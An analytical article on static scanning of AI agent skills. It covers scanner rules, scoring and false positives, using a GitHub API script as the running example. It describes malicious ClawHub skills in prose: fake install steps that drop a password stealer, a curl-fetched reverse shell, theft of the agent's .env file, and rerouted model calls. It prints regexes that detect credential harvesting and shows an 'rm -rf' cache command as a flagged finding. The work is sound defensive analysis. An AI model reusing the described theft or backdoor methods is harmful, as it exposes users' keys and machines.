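# Static analysis of agent skill code: network imports, environment variables and false positives

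## What is an agent skill, and why do scanners look at its network and credential code?

An agent skill is a folder of instructions, often with scripts, that an AI agent can load when a task calls for it. An agent is a program built around a language model that can open files, run commands and call online services for its user. Claude Code, OpenClaw and Hermes Agent all load skills. Anthropic introduced skills in Claude Code in October 2025 and made the format an open standard that December.

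Public collections of skills grew quickly. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) counted 170,226 skills in February 2026 on skillsmp.com, a registry where users find or install skills. In *Do Not Mention This to the User*, Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) studied the same registry and a smaller one, skills.rest, and found that neither vets the skills it lists.

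Users who want some protection can run a scanner, a program that inspects a skill and reports on it before installation. Two of the most common warnings are that the skill's code can use the network and that it reads an environment variable whose name suggests a credential. Both warnings apply to code that steals keys, but also to nearly every legitimate program that uses an online service.

### What the folder holds

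The Agent Skills *Specification*, an open standard, requires only one file in a skill, SKILL.md. This file starts with a short block of structured fields (the frontmatter), followed by instructions in Markdown. An author may add a `scripts/` directory for executable code, `references/` for longer documentation and `assets/` for templates and data.

The frontmatter must include a name and a description. An optional `compatibility` field takes up to 500 characters of free text, and one of the standard's examples is "Requires git, docker, jq, and access to the internet". The base format has no field for API keys or environment variables, but it has a `metadata` map that the makers of each agent can use as they like.

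OpenClaw's *Skill format* describes an example skill that manages tasks in the to-do service Todoist. The skill's metadata lists `TODOIST_API_KEY` as a variable that must exist before the skill can run. ClawHub, OpenClaw's public registry, compares such declarations with the code and flags any variable that the code uses but the metadata omits. Nous Research's *Creating Skills*, the guide for Hermes Agent, describes a similar list called `required_environment_variables`, where the author can also note what each key is for. In both systems the declaration is the author's own claim, and OpenClaw will also load a skill that has no such metadata.

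### How an agent loads a skill and runs its scripts

An agent loads a skill in stages, mostly to save space in the model's context window (the text the model can take into account at one time). At startup, the agent puts the name and description of every installed skill into its system prompt, using roughly 100 tokens for each. If a task seems to match a skill, the agent reads the whole SKILL.md. It opens or runs the skill's other files only when the instructions call for them.

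The last stage matters most for security because the model can run a script it has never read. Anthropic's *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* describes a PDF skill with a Python script that extracts form fields, and notes that Claude can run the script without loading it into context. This is efficient, but it gives the model no chance to notice suspicious code in the script. A scan before installation may be the only time anyone or anything examines it.

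Once started, the script is an ordinary process on the user's computer. According to Liu and colleagues, code called through function calling or the Model Context Protocol (a standard for connecting models to outside tools) runs on a server, while a skill runs locally with the user's privileges. Chen and colleagues borrow the term "ambient authority" for this arrangement, in which the script inherits every right of the process that started it and nobody approves its access to each credential. A script that fetches the weather can therefore read any cloud keys that the user can read.

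In *Running OpenClaw safely* (2026), Microsoft's security researchers call installing a skill "basically installing privileged code" and advise against running OpenClaw on a normal workstation. OpenClaw's own documentation page, *Skills*, tells users to treat third-party skills as untrusted code, to read them before enabling them, and to prefer a sandbox (a closed-off environment with fewer rights) for risky tools.

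### Why keys sit in environment variables

An online service usually identifies a customer by an API key, a long secret string that the customer's program sends with each request. A skill's author cannot sensibly write the key into the code, because the code is public and each user has a different key. Chen and colleagues still found credentials written into the files of 107 skills in a sample of 17,022.

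A script usually gets its API key from an environment variable, a named value that the operating system passes to a program when the program starts. The user sets the key once, and the script reads it by name, with `os.environ["TODOIST_API_KEY"]` in Python or `process.env.TODOIST_API_KEY` in JavaScript. The same code works for every user without containing anyone's key.

By default, though, a program passes a copy of its whole environment to each program it starts. A script launched by the agent receives the Todoist key it needs and any other key in the agent's environment. OpenClaw, for example, applies the keys the user has configured for skills to its own process environment at the start of an agent run, and restores the original environment when the run ends. During the run, a script from one skill could in principle read a key the user supplied for another.

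It is fair to say that any script running directly on the user's machine can read the keys, but sandboxes limit this access. OpenClaw's injected keys have no effect inside its sandbox. Hermes Agent automatically passes into its sandboxes only the variables that a loaded skill has declared, though the user can add others by hand. To read an unrelated key, a skill would therefore normally have to name it in its own frontmatter, where a reviewer can see it.

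Many users keep their keys in a text file, usually named `.env`, and the agent loads them from there into environment variables. A thief can then steal the keys from either the file or the environment.

### Why scanners look for two signals

To steal a key, code has to read the secret, and then something has to send it to a party the owner did not authorise, which is called exfiltration. A script that reads every variable but sends nothing, or that opens connections but never touches a secret, does not steal a key by itself.

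Rule writers therefore cover reading credentials and sending data separately. Liu and colleagues use one pattern, "credential harvesting", for code that accesses environment variables commonly used for keys and tokens, and another, "external transmission", for web requests that may carry sensitive data to an outside domain. Of the 157 skills they confirmed as malicious, 58 contained both. Skills with credential harvesting had 2.24 times the odds of also containing external transmission.

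Scanners also check network code because a skill can download and run an outside program, which can steal data even if the skill's own code does not. Unit 42, the threat research group of Palo Alto Networks, points out that a malicious skill does not always need to take the key, because it can act through the agent's own authenticated sessions.

Still, these two signals together are much weaker evidence than they seem. The legitimate Todoist client also reads a key and sends it over the network, because Todoist uses the key to identify the user. A malicious skill differs in where it sends the key and whether the user agreed to that, and lists of imported libraries and variable names don't show either. Watching the program run isn't enough by itself either. Chen and colleagues ran their candidate skills with fake credentials, and 1,427 showed at least one suspicious indicator. Three reviewers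 then compared the behaviour with each skill's documentation and judged 907 of the 1,427 benign.

### The ClawHub case of February 2026

The best-known incident so far is a useful test of the two signals. Koi Security, which sells monitoring for installed software, audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub. Its report *ClawHavoc* classed 341 of them as malicious. According to The Hacker News, publishing there required little more than a week-old GitHub account.

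Nearly all of the 341 skills relied on fake installation steps. Koi attributes 335 of them to a single campaign. These skills posed as crypto wallets, YouTube tools and similar software, and their documentation had a "Prerequisites" section that asked the user to install something first. On Windows, this was a trojan in a password-protected archive, whose contents antivirus programs cannot scan. On macOS, the user had to copy a command from a web page and paste it into the terminal. After two further downloads, the command installed Atomic Stealer, a commercial program that steals passwords, browser data, crypto wallets and SSH keys. Three more skills used the same trick with an invented "AuthTool".

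A check for network and environment code had nothing relevant to match in these 338 skills, because the attack was text addressed to the reader and the program that did the stealing was never in the folder.

Two others, `better-polymarket` and `polymarket-all-in-one`, contained what looked like working code for searching a prediction market. A single instruction around line 180 fetched a script from the attacker's server and ran it, which gave the attacker an interactive shell on the machine. The next statement used the `requests` library for the market search. A rule for network imports would have correctly flagged `requests`, and a reviewer who followed up that finding would have found a good explanation for it. The backdoor called the command-line tool `curl` through the operating system and used no network library.

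The remaining skill, `rankaj`, was supposedly a weather tool. It read `~/.clawdbot/.env`, the agent's own credential file (Clawdbot is an earlier name for OpenClaw), and posted the contents to an address at webhook.site. The two signals are meant to catch this kind of theft, but only the network signal clearly works here. A network rule that covers JavaScript could have detected the outgoing request. A rule for `process.env` would not have matched the theft code that Koi published, because that code read the credentials from a file. A rule that also covers `.env` paths would have matched.

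By Koi's account, a network check could have flagged three of the 341 skills, only one of them for the right reason, and a strict environment-variable check could have flagged none. I would not read this as a general detection rate, because 335 of the skills are near-copies from one campaign and so reflect one attacker's choice of method.

Koi has a product to sell and advertises its free checking tool in the same post, but it also published the name of every skill it accused, along with file hashes and server addresses, so others can check its work. By 16 February, ClawHub had grown past 10,700 skills and Koi's count had reached 824. The mix of methods looks different in other registries. The 58 skills in which Liu and colleagues found both signals came from the two other registries they studied.

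### Findings, verdicts and the ways to be wrong

Static analysis means examining code without running it. It can be as simple as searching for the words `import requests` or as complex as tracing where a value can travel through a program. Cloud Security Alliance's *OpenClaw Threat Model* describes a simple scanner in OpenClaw's own source code that checks skills line by line against rules for dangerous patterns. Static analysis is quick, works before installation, and covers parts of a program that a test run might never reach. But it can only show what the code is able to do. Some scanners add other methods, such as a language model that reads the skill's instructions.

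A rule is one test that a scanner applies. A finding is one report that a rule matched at a given place, for example that line 12 of a script imports `requests`. A verdict is the judgement that the whole skill is safe, suspicious or malicious. It is easy to mistake findings for verdicts, and this causes much of the confusion about scanner accuracy.

A false positive is a harmless line reported as a threat in a finding, or a harmless skill reported as one in a verdict. A false negative is a malicious line or skill that the scanner lets through. A benign true positive is a finding that correctly describes legitimate behaviour, such as a report that the Todoist client reads `TODOIST_API_KEY`. Calling that finding a false positive suggests that the rule misfired and that a more precise pattern would fix it, but the rule worked as intended.

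For verdicts, a few numbers capture most of what a user needs. Take 100 imaginary skills, of which 10 are malicious, and a scanner that flags a skill as a threat whenever it finds both signals:

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious | 8 | 2 | 10 |
| Harmless | 36 | 54 | 90 |
| Total | 44 | 56 | 100 |

The 36 harmless skills the scanner flags are false positives, and the 2 malicious ones it misses are false negatives. Precision is the share of flagged skills that are malicious, here 8 of 44, or 18 per cent. Recall is the share of malicious skills that the scanner flags, here 8 of 10, or 80 per cent. The base rate is the share of all skills that are malicious, here 10 per cent.

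Precision depends heavily on the base rate. Suppose a scanner catches 80 per cent of malicious skills and wrongly flags 40 per cent of harmless ones. If it scans 1,000 skills, of which 10 are malicious, it catches 8 of them but also flags 396 harmless skills, so its precision is 2 per cent. If it scans 100 skills with the same rules and half are malicious, its precision is 67 per cent.

A published precision figure therefore means little unless the reader knows what proportion of the tested skills were malicious. Liu and colleagues report 99.6 per cent precision for their full method, which combines static rules with test runs, on a set of 150 malicious and 150 benign skills. In Koi's first audit of ClawHub, about 12 per cent of the skills were malicious.

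## How does a scanner decide that an import or an environment read is suspicious?

A scanner can treat code as plain text or parse it and examine its structure. In both cases, it compares the code with predefined lists, such as the names of network libraries and words common in the names of secrets.

For example, a skill might summarise the open issues of a GitHub project. Its SKILL.md contains instructions for the agent to run the script below and write a summary from the output.

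```python
import os
import sys
import requests

token = os.environ["GITHUB_TOKEN"]
headers = {"Authorization": f"Bearer {token}"}

def open_issues(repo):
    r = requests.get(f"https://api.github.com/repos/{repo}/issues", headers=headers)
    r.raise_for_status()
    return r.json()

for issue in open_issues(sys.argv[1]):
    print(issue["number"], issue["title"])
```

Line 3 (counting blank lines) imports a network library, and line 5 reads the user's GitHub token from the environment. Line 6 puts the token into a header, and line 9 sends that header to GitHub with a request for the issues. The token lets the skill work on private projects too. As with the Todoist client, the credential goes only to the service that issued it.

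### Text patterns

The simplest kind of rule is a regular expression, a compact notation for a pattern of characters. Liu and colleagues published simplified versions of the 14 patterns with which they picked out suspicious skills. E1 is their rule for external transmission and E2 their rule for credential harvesting:

```
E1   requests.(post|put|get).*http[s]?://(?!localhost)
E2   os.(environ|getenv).*(?i)(key|secret|token|password|api)
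```

E1 reads from left to right as follows:

- `requests` matches exactly those letters.
- `.` matches any single character except a line break. Here it stands for the full stop in `requests.get`, though a strict pattern would write `\.` for that.
- `(post|put|get)` matches any one of the three words. The bars mean "or".
- `.*` matches any number of characters, up to the end of the line.
- `http[s]?://` matches `http://` or `https://`, because the question mark makes the `s` optional.
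- `(?!localhost)` rejects the match if the next characters are `localhost`, the usual name for the user's own machine.

Line 9 of the GitHub script has `requests.get(` followed by a quoted URL that starts with `https://` and does not continue with `localhost`, so E1 reports it. E1 does not report line 3, which is only an import, because the rule requires a call and an address.

E2 matches `os`, again followed by any one character, and then `environ` or `getenv`, Python's two usual ways of reading an environment variable. The `.*` allows any other characters to follow on the line, `(?i)` makes the match ignore case, and the last group lists five words, one of which must appear. Line 5 contains `os.environ` and, a few characters later, `TOKEN`, so E2 reports it.

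E2 relies entirely on the five words to decide what counts as a secret, so its results are rough. It also matches `os.environ["API_REGION"]`, which probably holds the name of a data centre, and `os.environ["KEYBOARD_LAYOUT"]`, because "keyboard" begins with "key". Since `.*` runs to the end of the line, a comment on the same line containing the word "key" is enough to trigger a match. But E2 would miss the same credential if the author had named the variable `GITHUB_PAT`, for "personal access token".

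E1 also depends on layout. If the author stores `https://api.github.com` in a constant at the top of the file and writes `requests.get(API + path)` further down, the call and the address are on different lines and E1 finds nothing. A formatter can have the same effect by splitting the call. Python's style guide recommends lines of at most 79 characters and line 9 has 84, so a formatter with that limit would move the address to the next line and remove the finding without changing how the script behaves.

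Liu and colleagues rate E1 as HIGH and E2 as CRITICAL. CRITICAL means an immediate threat with a high impact, the same rating they give to opening SSH key files or downloading a remote script and running it. The rating applies to the pattern regardless of what the surrounding code does with the value, so line 5 is rated CRITICAL just like a line that reads a cloud key to steal it.

Liu and colleagues describe the two printed rules as simplified and say the full implementation handles further edge cases. The printed E2 would fail to compile in Python 3.11, which they list among the study's software, because that version accepts `(?i)` only at the beginning of a pattern. All 14 patterns together also matched only 4.4 per cent of 98,380 skills, which is hard to believe of the printed set because it includes a pattern for any line where "always" or "must" comes before "run". The rules that ran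 were probably narrower, but the printed version doesn't show how much narrower E2 was, which matters a great deal for legitimate API clients.

### Syntax trees

A parser turns source code into a syntax tree, a nested description of the program's parts. Python builds one whenever it runs a script, and its standard `ast` module lets other programs access it. Line 3 becomes an `Import` node with the module name `requests`. The right-hand side of line 5 becomes a `Subscript` node (a lookup in square brackets) on the attribute `environ` of the name `os`, with the constant `"GITHUB_TOKEN"` inside. Line 9 contains a `Call` node whose function is the attribute `get` of the name `requests`.

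A tree rule might report every `Import` node whose module is on a list, or every lookup in `os.environ` whose constant contains a word such as "token". KodeAgent, a coding agent, has a small detector that works this way. It walks through the tree of Python code and records any access to environment variables, system commands, and calls that run text as code. The detector is a backup to a review by a language model.

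Checking the syntax tree avoids several errors of text matching. E1 matches an old `requests.get("https://...")` left in a comment, but the tree omits comments. A call that spans several lines is still one node. If a script begins with `import requests as rq`, the `Import` node stores both names, so a rule that tracks them can recognise `rq.get` later. A tree rule can also follow `from os import environ` to a later `environ["GITHUB_TOKEN"]`, which E2 misses because it looks for `os.`.

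Text rules also fail to distinguish functions that share a name. Python's `exec()` runs text as code, which is a good reason to look closely, while the `exec` method of a JavaScript regular expression only searches text for a pattern. The release notes for NVIDIA's *SkillSpector v2.5.3* (2026), an open-source scanner for agent skills, list a fix for false positives on this method. In the same release, NVIDIA let several steps of the scanner share one parsed tree of each Python file so that they would identify environment reads more consistently.

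Each programming language needs its own parser, though, and a file with a syntax error produces no syntax tree. SKILL.md is even harder to parse because it mixes prose with code snippets in any language. Scanners therefore tend to check all files for text patterns and apply syntax-tree rules only to the code they can parse.

A tree rule helps little with the GitHub script. It would report the import on line 3, the environment read on line 5 and the call on line 9, all benign true positives.

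### Which names are on the lists

Scanner makers disagree about how much code justifies a network finding. Some rules flag an import alone. Liu and colleagues reviewed the false positives of Cisco's scanner and found that it had classified the line `from urllib.request import Request` as attempted network exfiltration. That line cannot send anything, because `Request` only describes a request, and the script has to pass it to another function before any data leaves the machine.

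Mondoo, a security company, reports the call instead. One of its published scans lists lines such as `requests.get(url, headers=headers)` as a "network request primitive" that can transmit data externally. This rule is broader than E1, which would miss the line because the address is in a variable. Mondoo gives the finding low severity and 95 per cent confidence. The quoted line leaves little doubt that the code makes a network request, but it can't support a 95 per cent chance of data theft, which a reader could easily infer from the finding's category, "data exfiltration".

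The same scan reports undeclared network use as a separate finding, also of low severity. The GitHub script could trigger both findings, one for making the request and one for a field missing from the frontmatter. Counting findings is a poor way to compare skills because one harmless line can produce several.

### From findings to a verdict in Cisco's scanner

A scanner has to combine its findings into one judgement. Liu and colleagues give each skill the severity of its worst finding, so line 5 alone makes the GitHub skill CRITICAL. Their full method then adds a test run and a manual review, but a user who runs only static rules like these sees just the CRITICAL rating.

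Cisco's *Skill Scanner* gives each scan result a property called `is_safe`, which is true unless the scan produced a HIGH or CRITICAL finding. A skill with twenty MEDIUM findings therefore passes. Cisco warns that the property does not guarantee that a skill is free of risk, although the name suggests it does.

Cisco's overview lists eight analyzers in version 2.0.11. The static analyzer checks all files against text patterns, which are stored in YAML, a plain format for structured data, and YARA, a notation that malware analysts use to describe suspicious files. Another analyzer examines chained shell commands, and a third checks compiled Python files. These three run by default. The syntax-tree analyzer, which follows data through Python files, runs only with the option `--use-behavioral`. An ordinary scan of the GitHub script would therefore rely mainly on text patterns.

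The value of `is_safe` for this script depends on the severity that Cisco assigns to network calls and environment reads. Cisco's documentation for `defenseclaw`, a command that runs the scanner, gives some examples of severity levels. A production API key written into the code is CRITICAL, as is a tool that contacts a domain known for exfiltration. An obfuscated payload meant for the shell is HIGH, and a non-standard endpoint is MEDIUM. By those standards, a plain request to api.github.com should rank low. The `urllib` finding suggests that the scanner was once stricter, but Liu and colleagues do not give that finding's severity, and Cisco may have changed the rule since.

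The user can also change the verdict by choosing a different scan policy. Cisco offers three ready-made policies (strict, balanced and permissive), and organisations can write their own. An example policy file from Cisco specifies which rules apply to which kinds of file and includes a setting that lowers the severity of shell findings in documentation. Two people can therefore scan the same skill with the same scanner version and get different verdicts, so a verdict means little unless the policy is reported with it.

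### Points in NVIDIA's SkillSpector

NVIDIA's *SkillSpector* adds up points. Its README of May 2026 and NVIDIA's documentation page *scanning agent skills* both report 64 patterns in 16 categories. A later README, which Socket's *skillspector* page reproduces, has 68 patterns in 17 categories. It adds three patterns for instructions that stop a model from refusing and one for disguised calls to dangerous functions. The tool changes quickly; NVIDIA released version 2.5.3 on 4 August 2026 and version 2.9.2 six days later.

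NVIDIA built SkillSpector on an earlier study by Liu and colleagues, and it uses the labels E1 and E2 for the same two behaviours. It rates both as less severe than the study did: external transmission is MEDIUM instead of HIGH, and environment variable harvesting is HIGH instead of CRITICAL. Registry users also see these labels. For example, ClawHub's audit page for a skill called *Security Vulnerability Scanner* lists both among SkillSpector's patterns.

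SkillSpector also has rules based on syntax trees, but they mostly target calls that run commands or text as code. One rule reports `__import__()`, a function that loads a module while the program is running, and rates it HIGH. These rules don't report an ordinary `import requests` at the top of a file.

It is less clear what E2 covers in this scanner. NVIDIA describes it as "Collecting API keys and secrets", and the README illustrates it with a loop that begins `for key, val in os.environ.items():`. This loop goes through every environment variable, which is much stranger than reading one variable by name. The E2 rule printed by Liu and colleagues would not match the loop, because none of the rule's five words comes after `os.environ` on that line. Their rule clearly covers the named read in the GitHub script, but the README does not show whether SkillSpector's E2 also covers that read.

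Each CRITICAL finding adds 50 points, each HIGH finding 25, each MEDIUM finding 10 and each LOW finding 5. If the skill contains executable scripts, SkillSpector multiplies the result by 1.3. A score of up to 20 leads to the recommendation SAFE and a score from 21 to 50 to CAUTION. Anything higher means DO NOT INSTALL. The table applies this arithmetic to the GitHub skill for different sets of findings:

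| Findings | Points | Times 1.3 | Recommendation |
|---|---|---|---|
| E1 only | 10 | 13 | SAFE |
| E1 and E2 | 35 | 45.5 | CAUTION |
| E1, E2 and a missing permission declaration | 45 | 58.5 | DO NOT INSTALL |
| E1, E2 and a credential exfiltration chain | 85 | 110.5, above the maximum of 100 | DO NOT INSTALL |

Code that has detectable capabilities but no permissions field gets a MEDIUM finding for the missing declaration. NVIDIA lists this finding under its rules for the Model Context Protocol, so it may not apply to every skill. The last row is a data-flow rule for credentials that reach a network call, and its description fits lines 5 to 9 of the script.

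A harmless 14-line script can thus receive any of the three recommendations, depending on which rules it triggers. The step from CAUTION to DO NOT INSTALL matters most in automated use, because SkillSpector reports success to the calling program for scores up to 50 and failure for scores above 50. A gate that checks only this signal would install the skill in the second row without warning and block the one in the third, although the only difference between them is a missing line of metadata.

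This arithmetic is only approximate, because NVIDIA's sample report doesn't match it. The report rates a skill's two findings, E2 and E1, as HIGH, although the pattern table lists E1 as MEDIUM. It also gives a score of 78, while two HIGH findings with the multiplier make 65. If E1 does count as HIGH in practice, the GitHub script reaches 65 from E1 and E2 alone, and the recommendation becomes DO NOT INSTALL.

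### A weighted score and unusual imports

*SkillsMetric* (Chen, Ji and colleagues, 2026) describes a more elaborate system that examines the whole skill in five stages and combines the stage scores into a number from 0 to 100.

| Stage | What raises the score | Weight |
|---|---|---|
| Pattern density | Matches of more than 50 weighted text patterns, relative to the length of the content | 0.15 |
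| Statistical anomaly | Bytes that look like encoded or encrypted data | 0.20 |
| Data flow | A credential that the code reads, transforms and sends | 0.30 |
| Import anomaly | An unusual combination of security-relevant packages | 0.15 |
| Capability mismatch | Behaviour that SKILL.md does not declare | 0.10 |

The system multiplies each stage score by its weight and adds the results. It then adds a bonus of 5 points if two stages respond to the same skill, or 10 points if three or more do. The statistical stage does not count towards the bonus, because encoded content usually triggers the pattern stage too, and the same evidence would be counted twice. The weights add up to 0.90, which leaves room for the bonus. The system flags any skill that scores 25 or more, and rates scores from 25 to 44 as MEDIUM, 45 to 69 as HIGH, and 70 or more as CRITICAL.

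Chen, Ji and colleagues set each stage's weight by hand after looking at how the stage behaved on harmless and malicious skills. Data flow has the largest weight because complete chains from reading data to sending it were rare in harmless code. Capability mismatch has the smallest because skill developers declare capabilities inconsistently. They add the stage scores instead of multiplying them because many attacks leave traces in only one or two stages, and a single zero would make the whole product zero. A sum also lets a reviewer see how many points each stage contributed.

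In its import stage, SkillsMetric checks whether a skill's combination of packages is unusual compared with a baseline of harmless skills. A plain module list, by contrast, flags `requests` in every script that imports it. Chen, Ji and colleagues give the example of `urllib` together with `base64` and `os`. This combination might worry a reviewer because `os` can read environment variables, `base64` can disguise their values as meaningless text, and `urllib` can send that text to another machine.

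In an invented example, 300 of 1,000 harmless scripts import both `os` and `requests`, while only 2 import `urllib`, `base64` and `os`. A rule based on this baseline would ignore the GitHub script and report the rarer combination. This improves on a module list because it doesn't flag ordinary API clients, but a rare combination can still be harmless. For example, basic authentication, a common way of logging in to a web service, requires the program to encode the user name and password in base64. An honest developer who wants to avoid third-party packages would use `urllib` for the request and `os` for the password, and the script would be reported.

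Much depends on the baseline, which Chen, Ji and colleagues describe in a single phrase. They do not explain which packages count as security-relevant, how many skills the baseline covers or how they turn rarity into a score. Their test set contains 2,000 harmless skills, of which only 400 came with scripts. If the baseline draws on the same skills, it is based on fairly few programs.

The malicious test skills may also make the import stage look more effective than it is. Chen, Ji and colleagues made 199 of the 266 by inserting an attack into a real, harmless skill. An inserted attack brings its own imports into a program that didn't need them, so the combination is likely to stand out. Someone who builds a data-stealing skill as an API client from the start would need no unusual imports. The average scores show that the import stage responds to attacks in code, but there is no comparison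 run without it, so its own contribution is unknown.

The weights limit the effect of a false alarm in the import stage. If each stage is scored from 0 to 100, as the totals imply, the import stage can add at most 15 points, which is not enough to flag a skill. A complete data-flow chain adds 30, which is enough by itself. The GitHub script reads a credential and sends it without encoding it, so its chain is incomplete, and the published description does not give the score for an incomplete chain. Suppose pattern density is 40 and the import stage finds nothing. With a data-flow score of 30, the total is 6 plus 9 plus a bonus of 5, or 20, and the skill passes. With a data-flow score of 50, the total is 26 and SkillsMetric flags the skill.

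Chen, Ji and colleagues justify the threshold of 25 with a scan of 138,133 real skills, in which 95 per cent scored below 16.77 and only 1.75 per cent reached 25. Because GitHub limits how many files a program may fetch, they scanned only the SKILL.md files and not the scripts, which contain most imports and environment reads. The low flag rate is therefore weak evidence about API clients like the GitHub skill, and the threshold might well need to be higher if their scripts were scanned too.

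## Why do these rules flag legitimate code?

Scanners warn about harmless code for two reasons. In a misreading, the finding is wrong about what the code does. It may report a network request that the script never makes, or a secret where the variable holds an ordinary setting. In a benign true positive, the finding describes the code correctly, but normal behaviour is mistaken for a threat, either in the verdict or by the person reading the finding.

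*Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* (2026), a study of the scanners that protect skill registries, makes a similar distinction in its advice on false positives. It advises scanner makers to check that flagged content shows the suspected behaviour and doesn't merely match a keyword, and to ask whether the operation, such as logging in to a service, serves the skill's purpose. It adds that a scanner's failure to inspect something is a reason for uncertainty, not evidence of malice.

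Better parsing can remove most misreadings. It does almost nothing for benign true positives, because there the scanner has already understood the code.

### Imports, names and assignments

Cisco's scanner misread a `urllib` import as attempted exfiltration. Scripts also collect imports they never use. An author switches from `requests` to `httpx` and forgets to delete the old line, or copies a block of imports from another project. A rule that matches imports reports network access whether or not the script uses them. A syntax-tree rule can flag an import only if a later call uses the imported name.

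But dropping all import findings would go too far, because Python runs a module's top-level code when a script first imports it. Python also searches the script's own folder before the installed packages, so if a skill includes a file called `requests.py` next to the script, `import requests` runs that file.

Variable names also cause false positives. A finance skill that reads `os.environ["STARTING_CAPITAL"]` triggers E2, the credential rule published by Liu and colleagues, because "capital" contains "api".

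A very common line in machine-learning code goes wrong twice. Hugging Face's tokenizers library, which splits text into units for a language model, prints a warning if a program starts a second process after the library has begun parallel work. Clay-Atlas' *solved huggingface tokenizers the current process just got forked* (2022), a programming blog's post on the warning, suggests this fix:

```python
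os.environ["TOKENIZERS_PARALLELISM"] = "false"
```

E2 matches because "tokenizers" begins with "token". But the variable is an on-off switch, and the line only writes to it, to silence a warning. Under the severity scheme that Liu and colleagues use, the script would still receive a CRITICAL finding for credential harvesting.

A syntax tree shows whether code reads an environment variable or assigns it. Python's parser labels each lookup in square brackets `Load` if the program reads the value and `Store` if it assigns one, so a rule can report only the `Load` cases. Assignments may deserve a separate rule, because a script that overwrites the variable holding a service's address can redirect every later request. Liu and colleagues found a malicious skill, Plan Refine, that sent all the agent's calls to Claude through the attacker's server.

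The parser can't determine whether a name refers to a secret, and each change to a rule's word list trades some errors for others. A rule could split names at the underscores and compare whole words, which would clear both `TOKENIZERS_PARALLELISM` and `STARTING_CAPITAL`. It would then miss `OPENAI_APIKEY`, which has no underscore between "API" and "KEY", unless the list also contained "apikey". Adding plurals to the list would catch a variable such as `SERVICE_TOKENS`, but it would also flag `MAX_TOKENS`, a common name for the maximum length of a model's answer.

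Function names also cause false positives. SkillSafe, which runs a registry and a scanner, had language-model agents review about 300 scans. Its *Ruleset v2026.06.05* (2026) reports that six rules accounted for most of the findings the agents dismissed. The noisiest rule was meant to catch Python's `compile()`, which turns text into executable code, but it also matched `re.compile()`, which only prepares a text pattern for searching. Some skills contained more than 15 `re.compile()` calls, and the rule flagged each one.

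SkillSafe's fix was to ignore `compile(`, `exec(` and `eval(` after a full stop. This simple change removes the false matches, but it also misses `builtins.exec(payload)`, which runs the payload just as `exec(payload)` does. A syntax-tree rule that tracks which object the method belongs to would avoid both the false matches and the missed calls.

The same scanner counted XML namespaces as network addresses. A Word document identifies its format with strings such as `http://www.w3.org/2001/XMLSchema`, which look like web addresses but serve as names. A program that edits documents can contain dozens of them without making any network requests. SkillSafe now removes these strings before it checks whether a file both accesses the network and runs commands.

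Some rules correctly detect that a program reads an environment variable and uses the network, but wrongly treat the variable's value as data being sent. In *False positive*, a complaint filed on GitHub, PaulieB14 objected to a warning that the developer's `subgraph-registry-mcp` combined environment access with a network send. According to the developer, the line reads `MCP_HTTP_PORT`, which sets the port where a local server listens and isn't sent to anyone. This is the developer's own account, though the variable's name fits it.

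### Cisco's false positives

Liu and colleagues reviewed false positives from Cisco's scanner by hand and traced them to three causes: the scanner matched names without checking what the call does, treated documentation and test files like production code, and flagged routine maintenance commands as attacks. The table lists their five examples, with the remedies from Cisco's *Advanced Features*, a guide to the scanner's settings.

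| Flagged code | Reported as | What went wrong | Setting in Cisco's guide |
|---|---|---|---|
| `re.compile()` | Code injection | Misreading: the call prepares a text pattern | None specific to this call |
| `curl -H "Authorization: Basic ..."` in SKILL.md | Credential exposure | Misreading: an example without a real credential | Filter for API documentation |
| `API_KEY = "test-key-123"` in a test | Leaked key | Misreading: the key is fake | Filters for test keys and placeholders |
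| `rm -rf /var/lib/apt/lists/*` | Destructive operation | Benign true positive: the command deletes files, but only a package cache | List of safe deletion targets |
| `from urllib.request import Request` | Network exfiltration | Misreading: the import sends nothing | None specific to imports |

Liu and colleagues attribute the last two rows to one cause, misinterpreted "operational patterns", but the two need different fixes. The cleanup command does delete files, so a scanner needs information showing that this folder is safe to empty. The import needs a rule that distinguishes loading a library from using it. Their list shows how the scanner failed, but they don't say how many false positives they examined or how many each cause explains.

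Cisco appears to have worked on the problem since. An older listing of the scanner, PyPI's *Security scanner for Agent Skills packages*, describes strict, balanced and permissive modes for one type of pattern and an option to disable individual rules. The current policies also let an organisation exempt documentation from selected rules, list known test keys, and name words such as "example" and "changeme" that mark a value as a placeholder. The default balanced policy filters out placeholders and API documentation. The strict policy turns the placeholder filter off, which allows more false positives.

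These settings at least partly address the documentation, test and maintenance cases, but coverage depends on what the lists contain. For example, the fake key `test-key-123` contains neither of the two placeholder words in Cisco's example policy, although the built-in lists may be longer. It is unclear from the guide whether Cisco has changed the rule for the `urllib` line. The optional data-flow analyzer could in principle tell an import from a transmission, but Cisco warns that no configuration removes all false positives.

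Filtering out documentation also carries a risk that it wouldn't in ordinary software, because an agent may carry out the commands in SKILL.md, whereas a README on GitHub is written for people to read. Liu and colleagues found 632 vulnerabilities in skills they had confirmed as malicious, and 84.2 per cent of those vulnerabilities were in SKILL.md files. A scanner that skips a `curl` command because it appears in documentation may therefore miss the attack.

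### What a better parser cannot settle

Even with a perfect parser, a scanner would report that the GitHub script reads a token and sends it out. Now change only the address on line 9:

```python
r = requests.get(f"https://api.github.com/repos/{repo}/issues", headers=headers)
r = requests.get(f"https://github-api.example/repos/{repo}/issues", headers=headers)
```

The two lines have syntax trees of the same shape and differ in one piece of text. The script leaks the user's token if a stranger owns the second domain, but it is fine if the user's employer runs that domain as a gateway to GitHub. Parsing can't distinguish these cases, because who owns a domain and what the user agreed to are facts outside the program.

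The scanner can only improve here by using outside knowledge. SkillSafe does this by comparing the variable's name with the destination's. If a script reads `BINANCE_API_KEY` and contacts only binance.com, SkillSafe treats the transfer as authentication and lowers the finding from high severity to information. The finding stays in the report, which seems right because it still describes the code correctly.

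Matching the variable's name to the domain works for many API clients, but not all. Hugging Face's usual variable, `HF_TOKEN`, has no word in common with its address, huggingface.co. A thief could also register a domain containing "binance" so that the names match. Matching names is therefore a reasonable way to decide which findings to read first, but a match is weak evidence that a skill is legitimate.

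JFrog's *Scanning AI Agent Skills*, the manual for a commercial scanner, defines a skill as malicious when there is high-confidence proof, and as suspicious when its behaviour could be malicious or benign depending on context that the scanner lacks. Its example policies block downloads of malicious skills but only notify the security team about suspicious ones. JFrog still rates every suspicious skill High severity, so a company that blocks everything rated High will also block skills that may be benign.

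### API clients, cloud tools and telemetry

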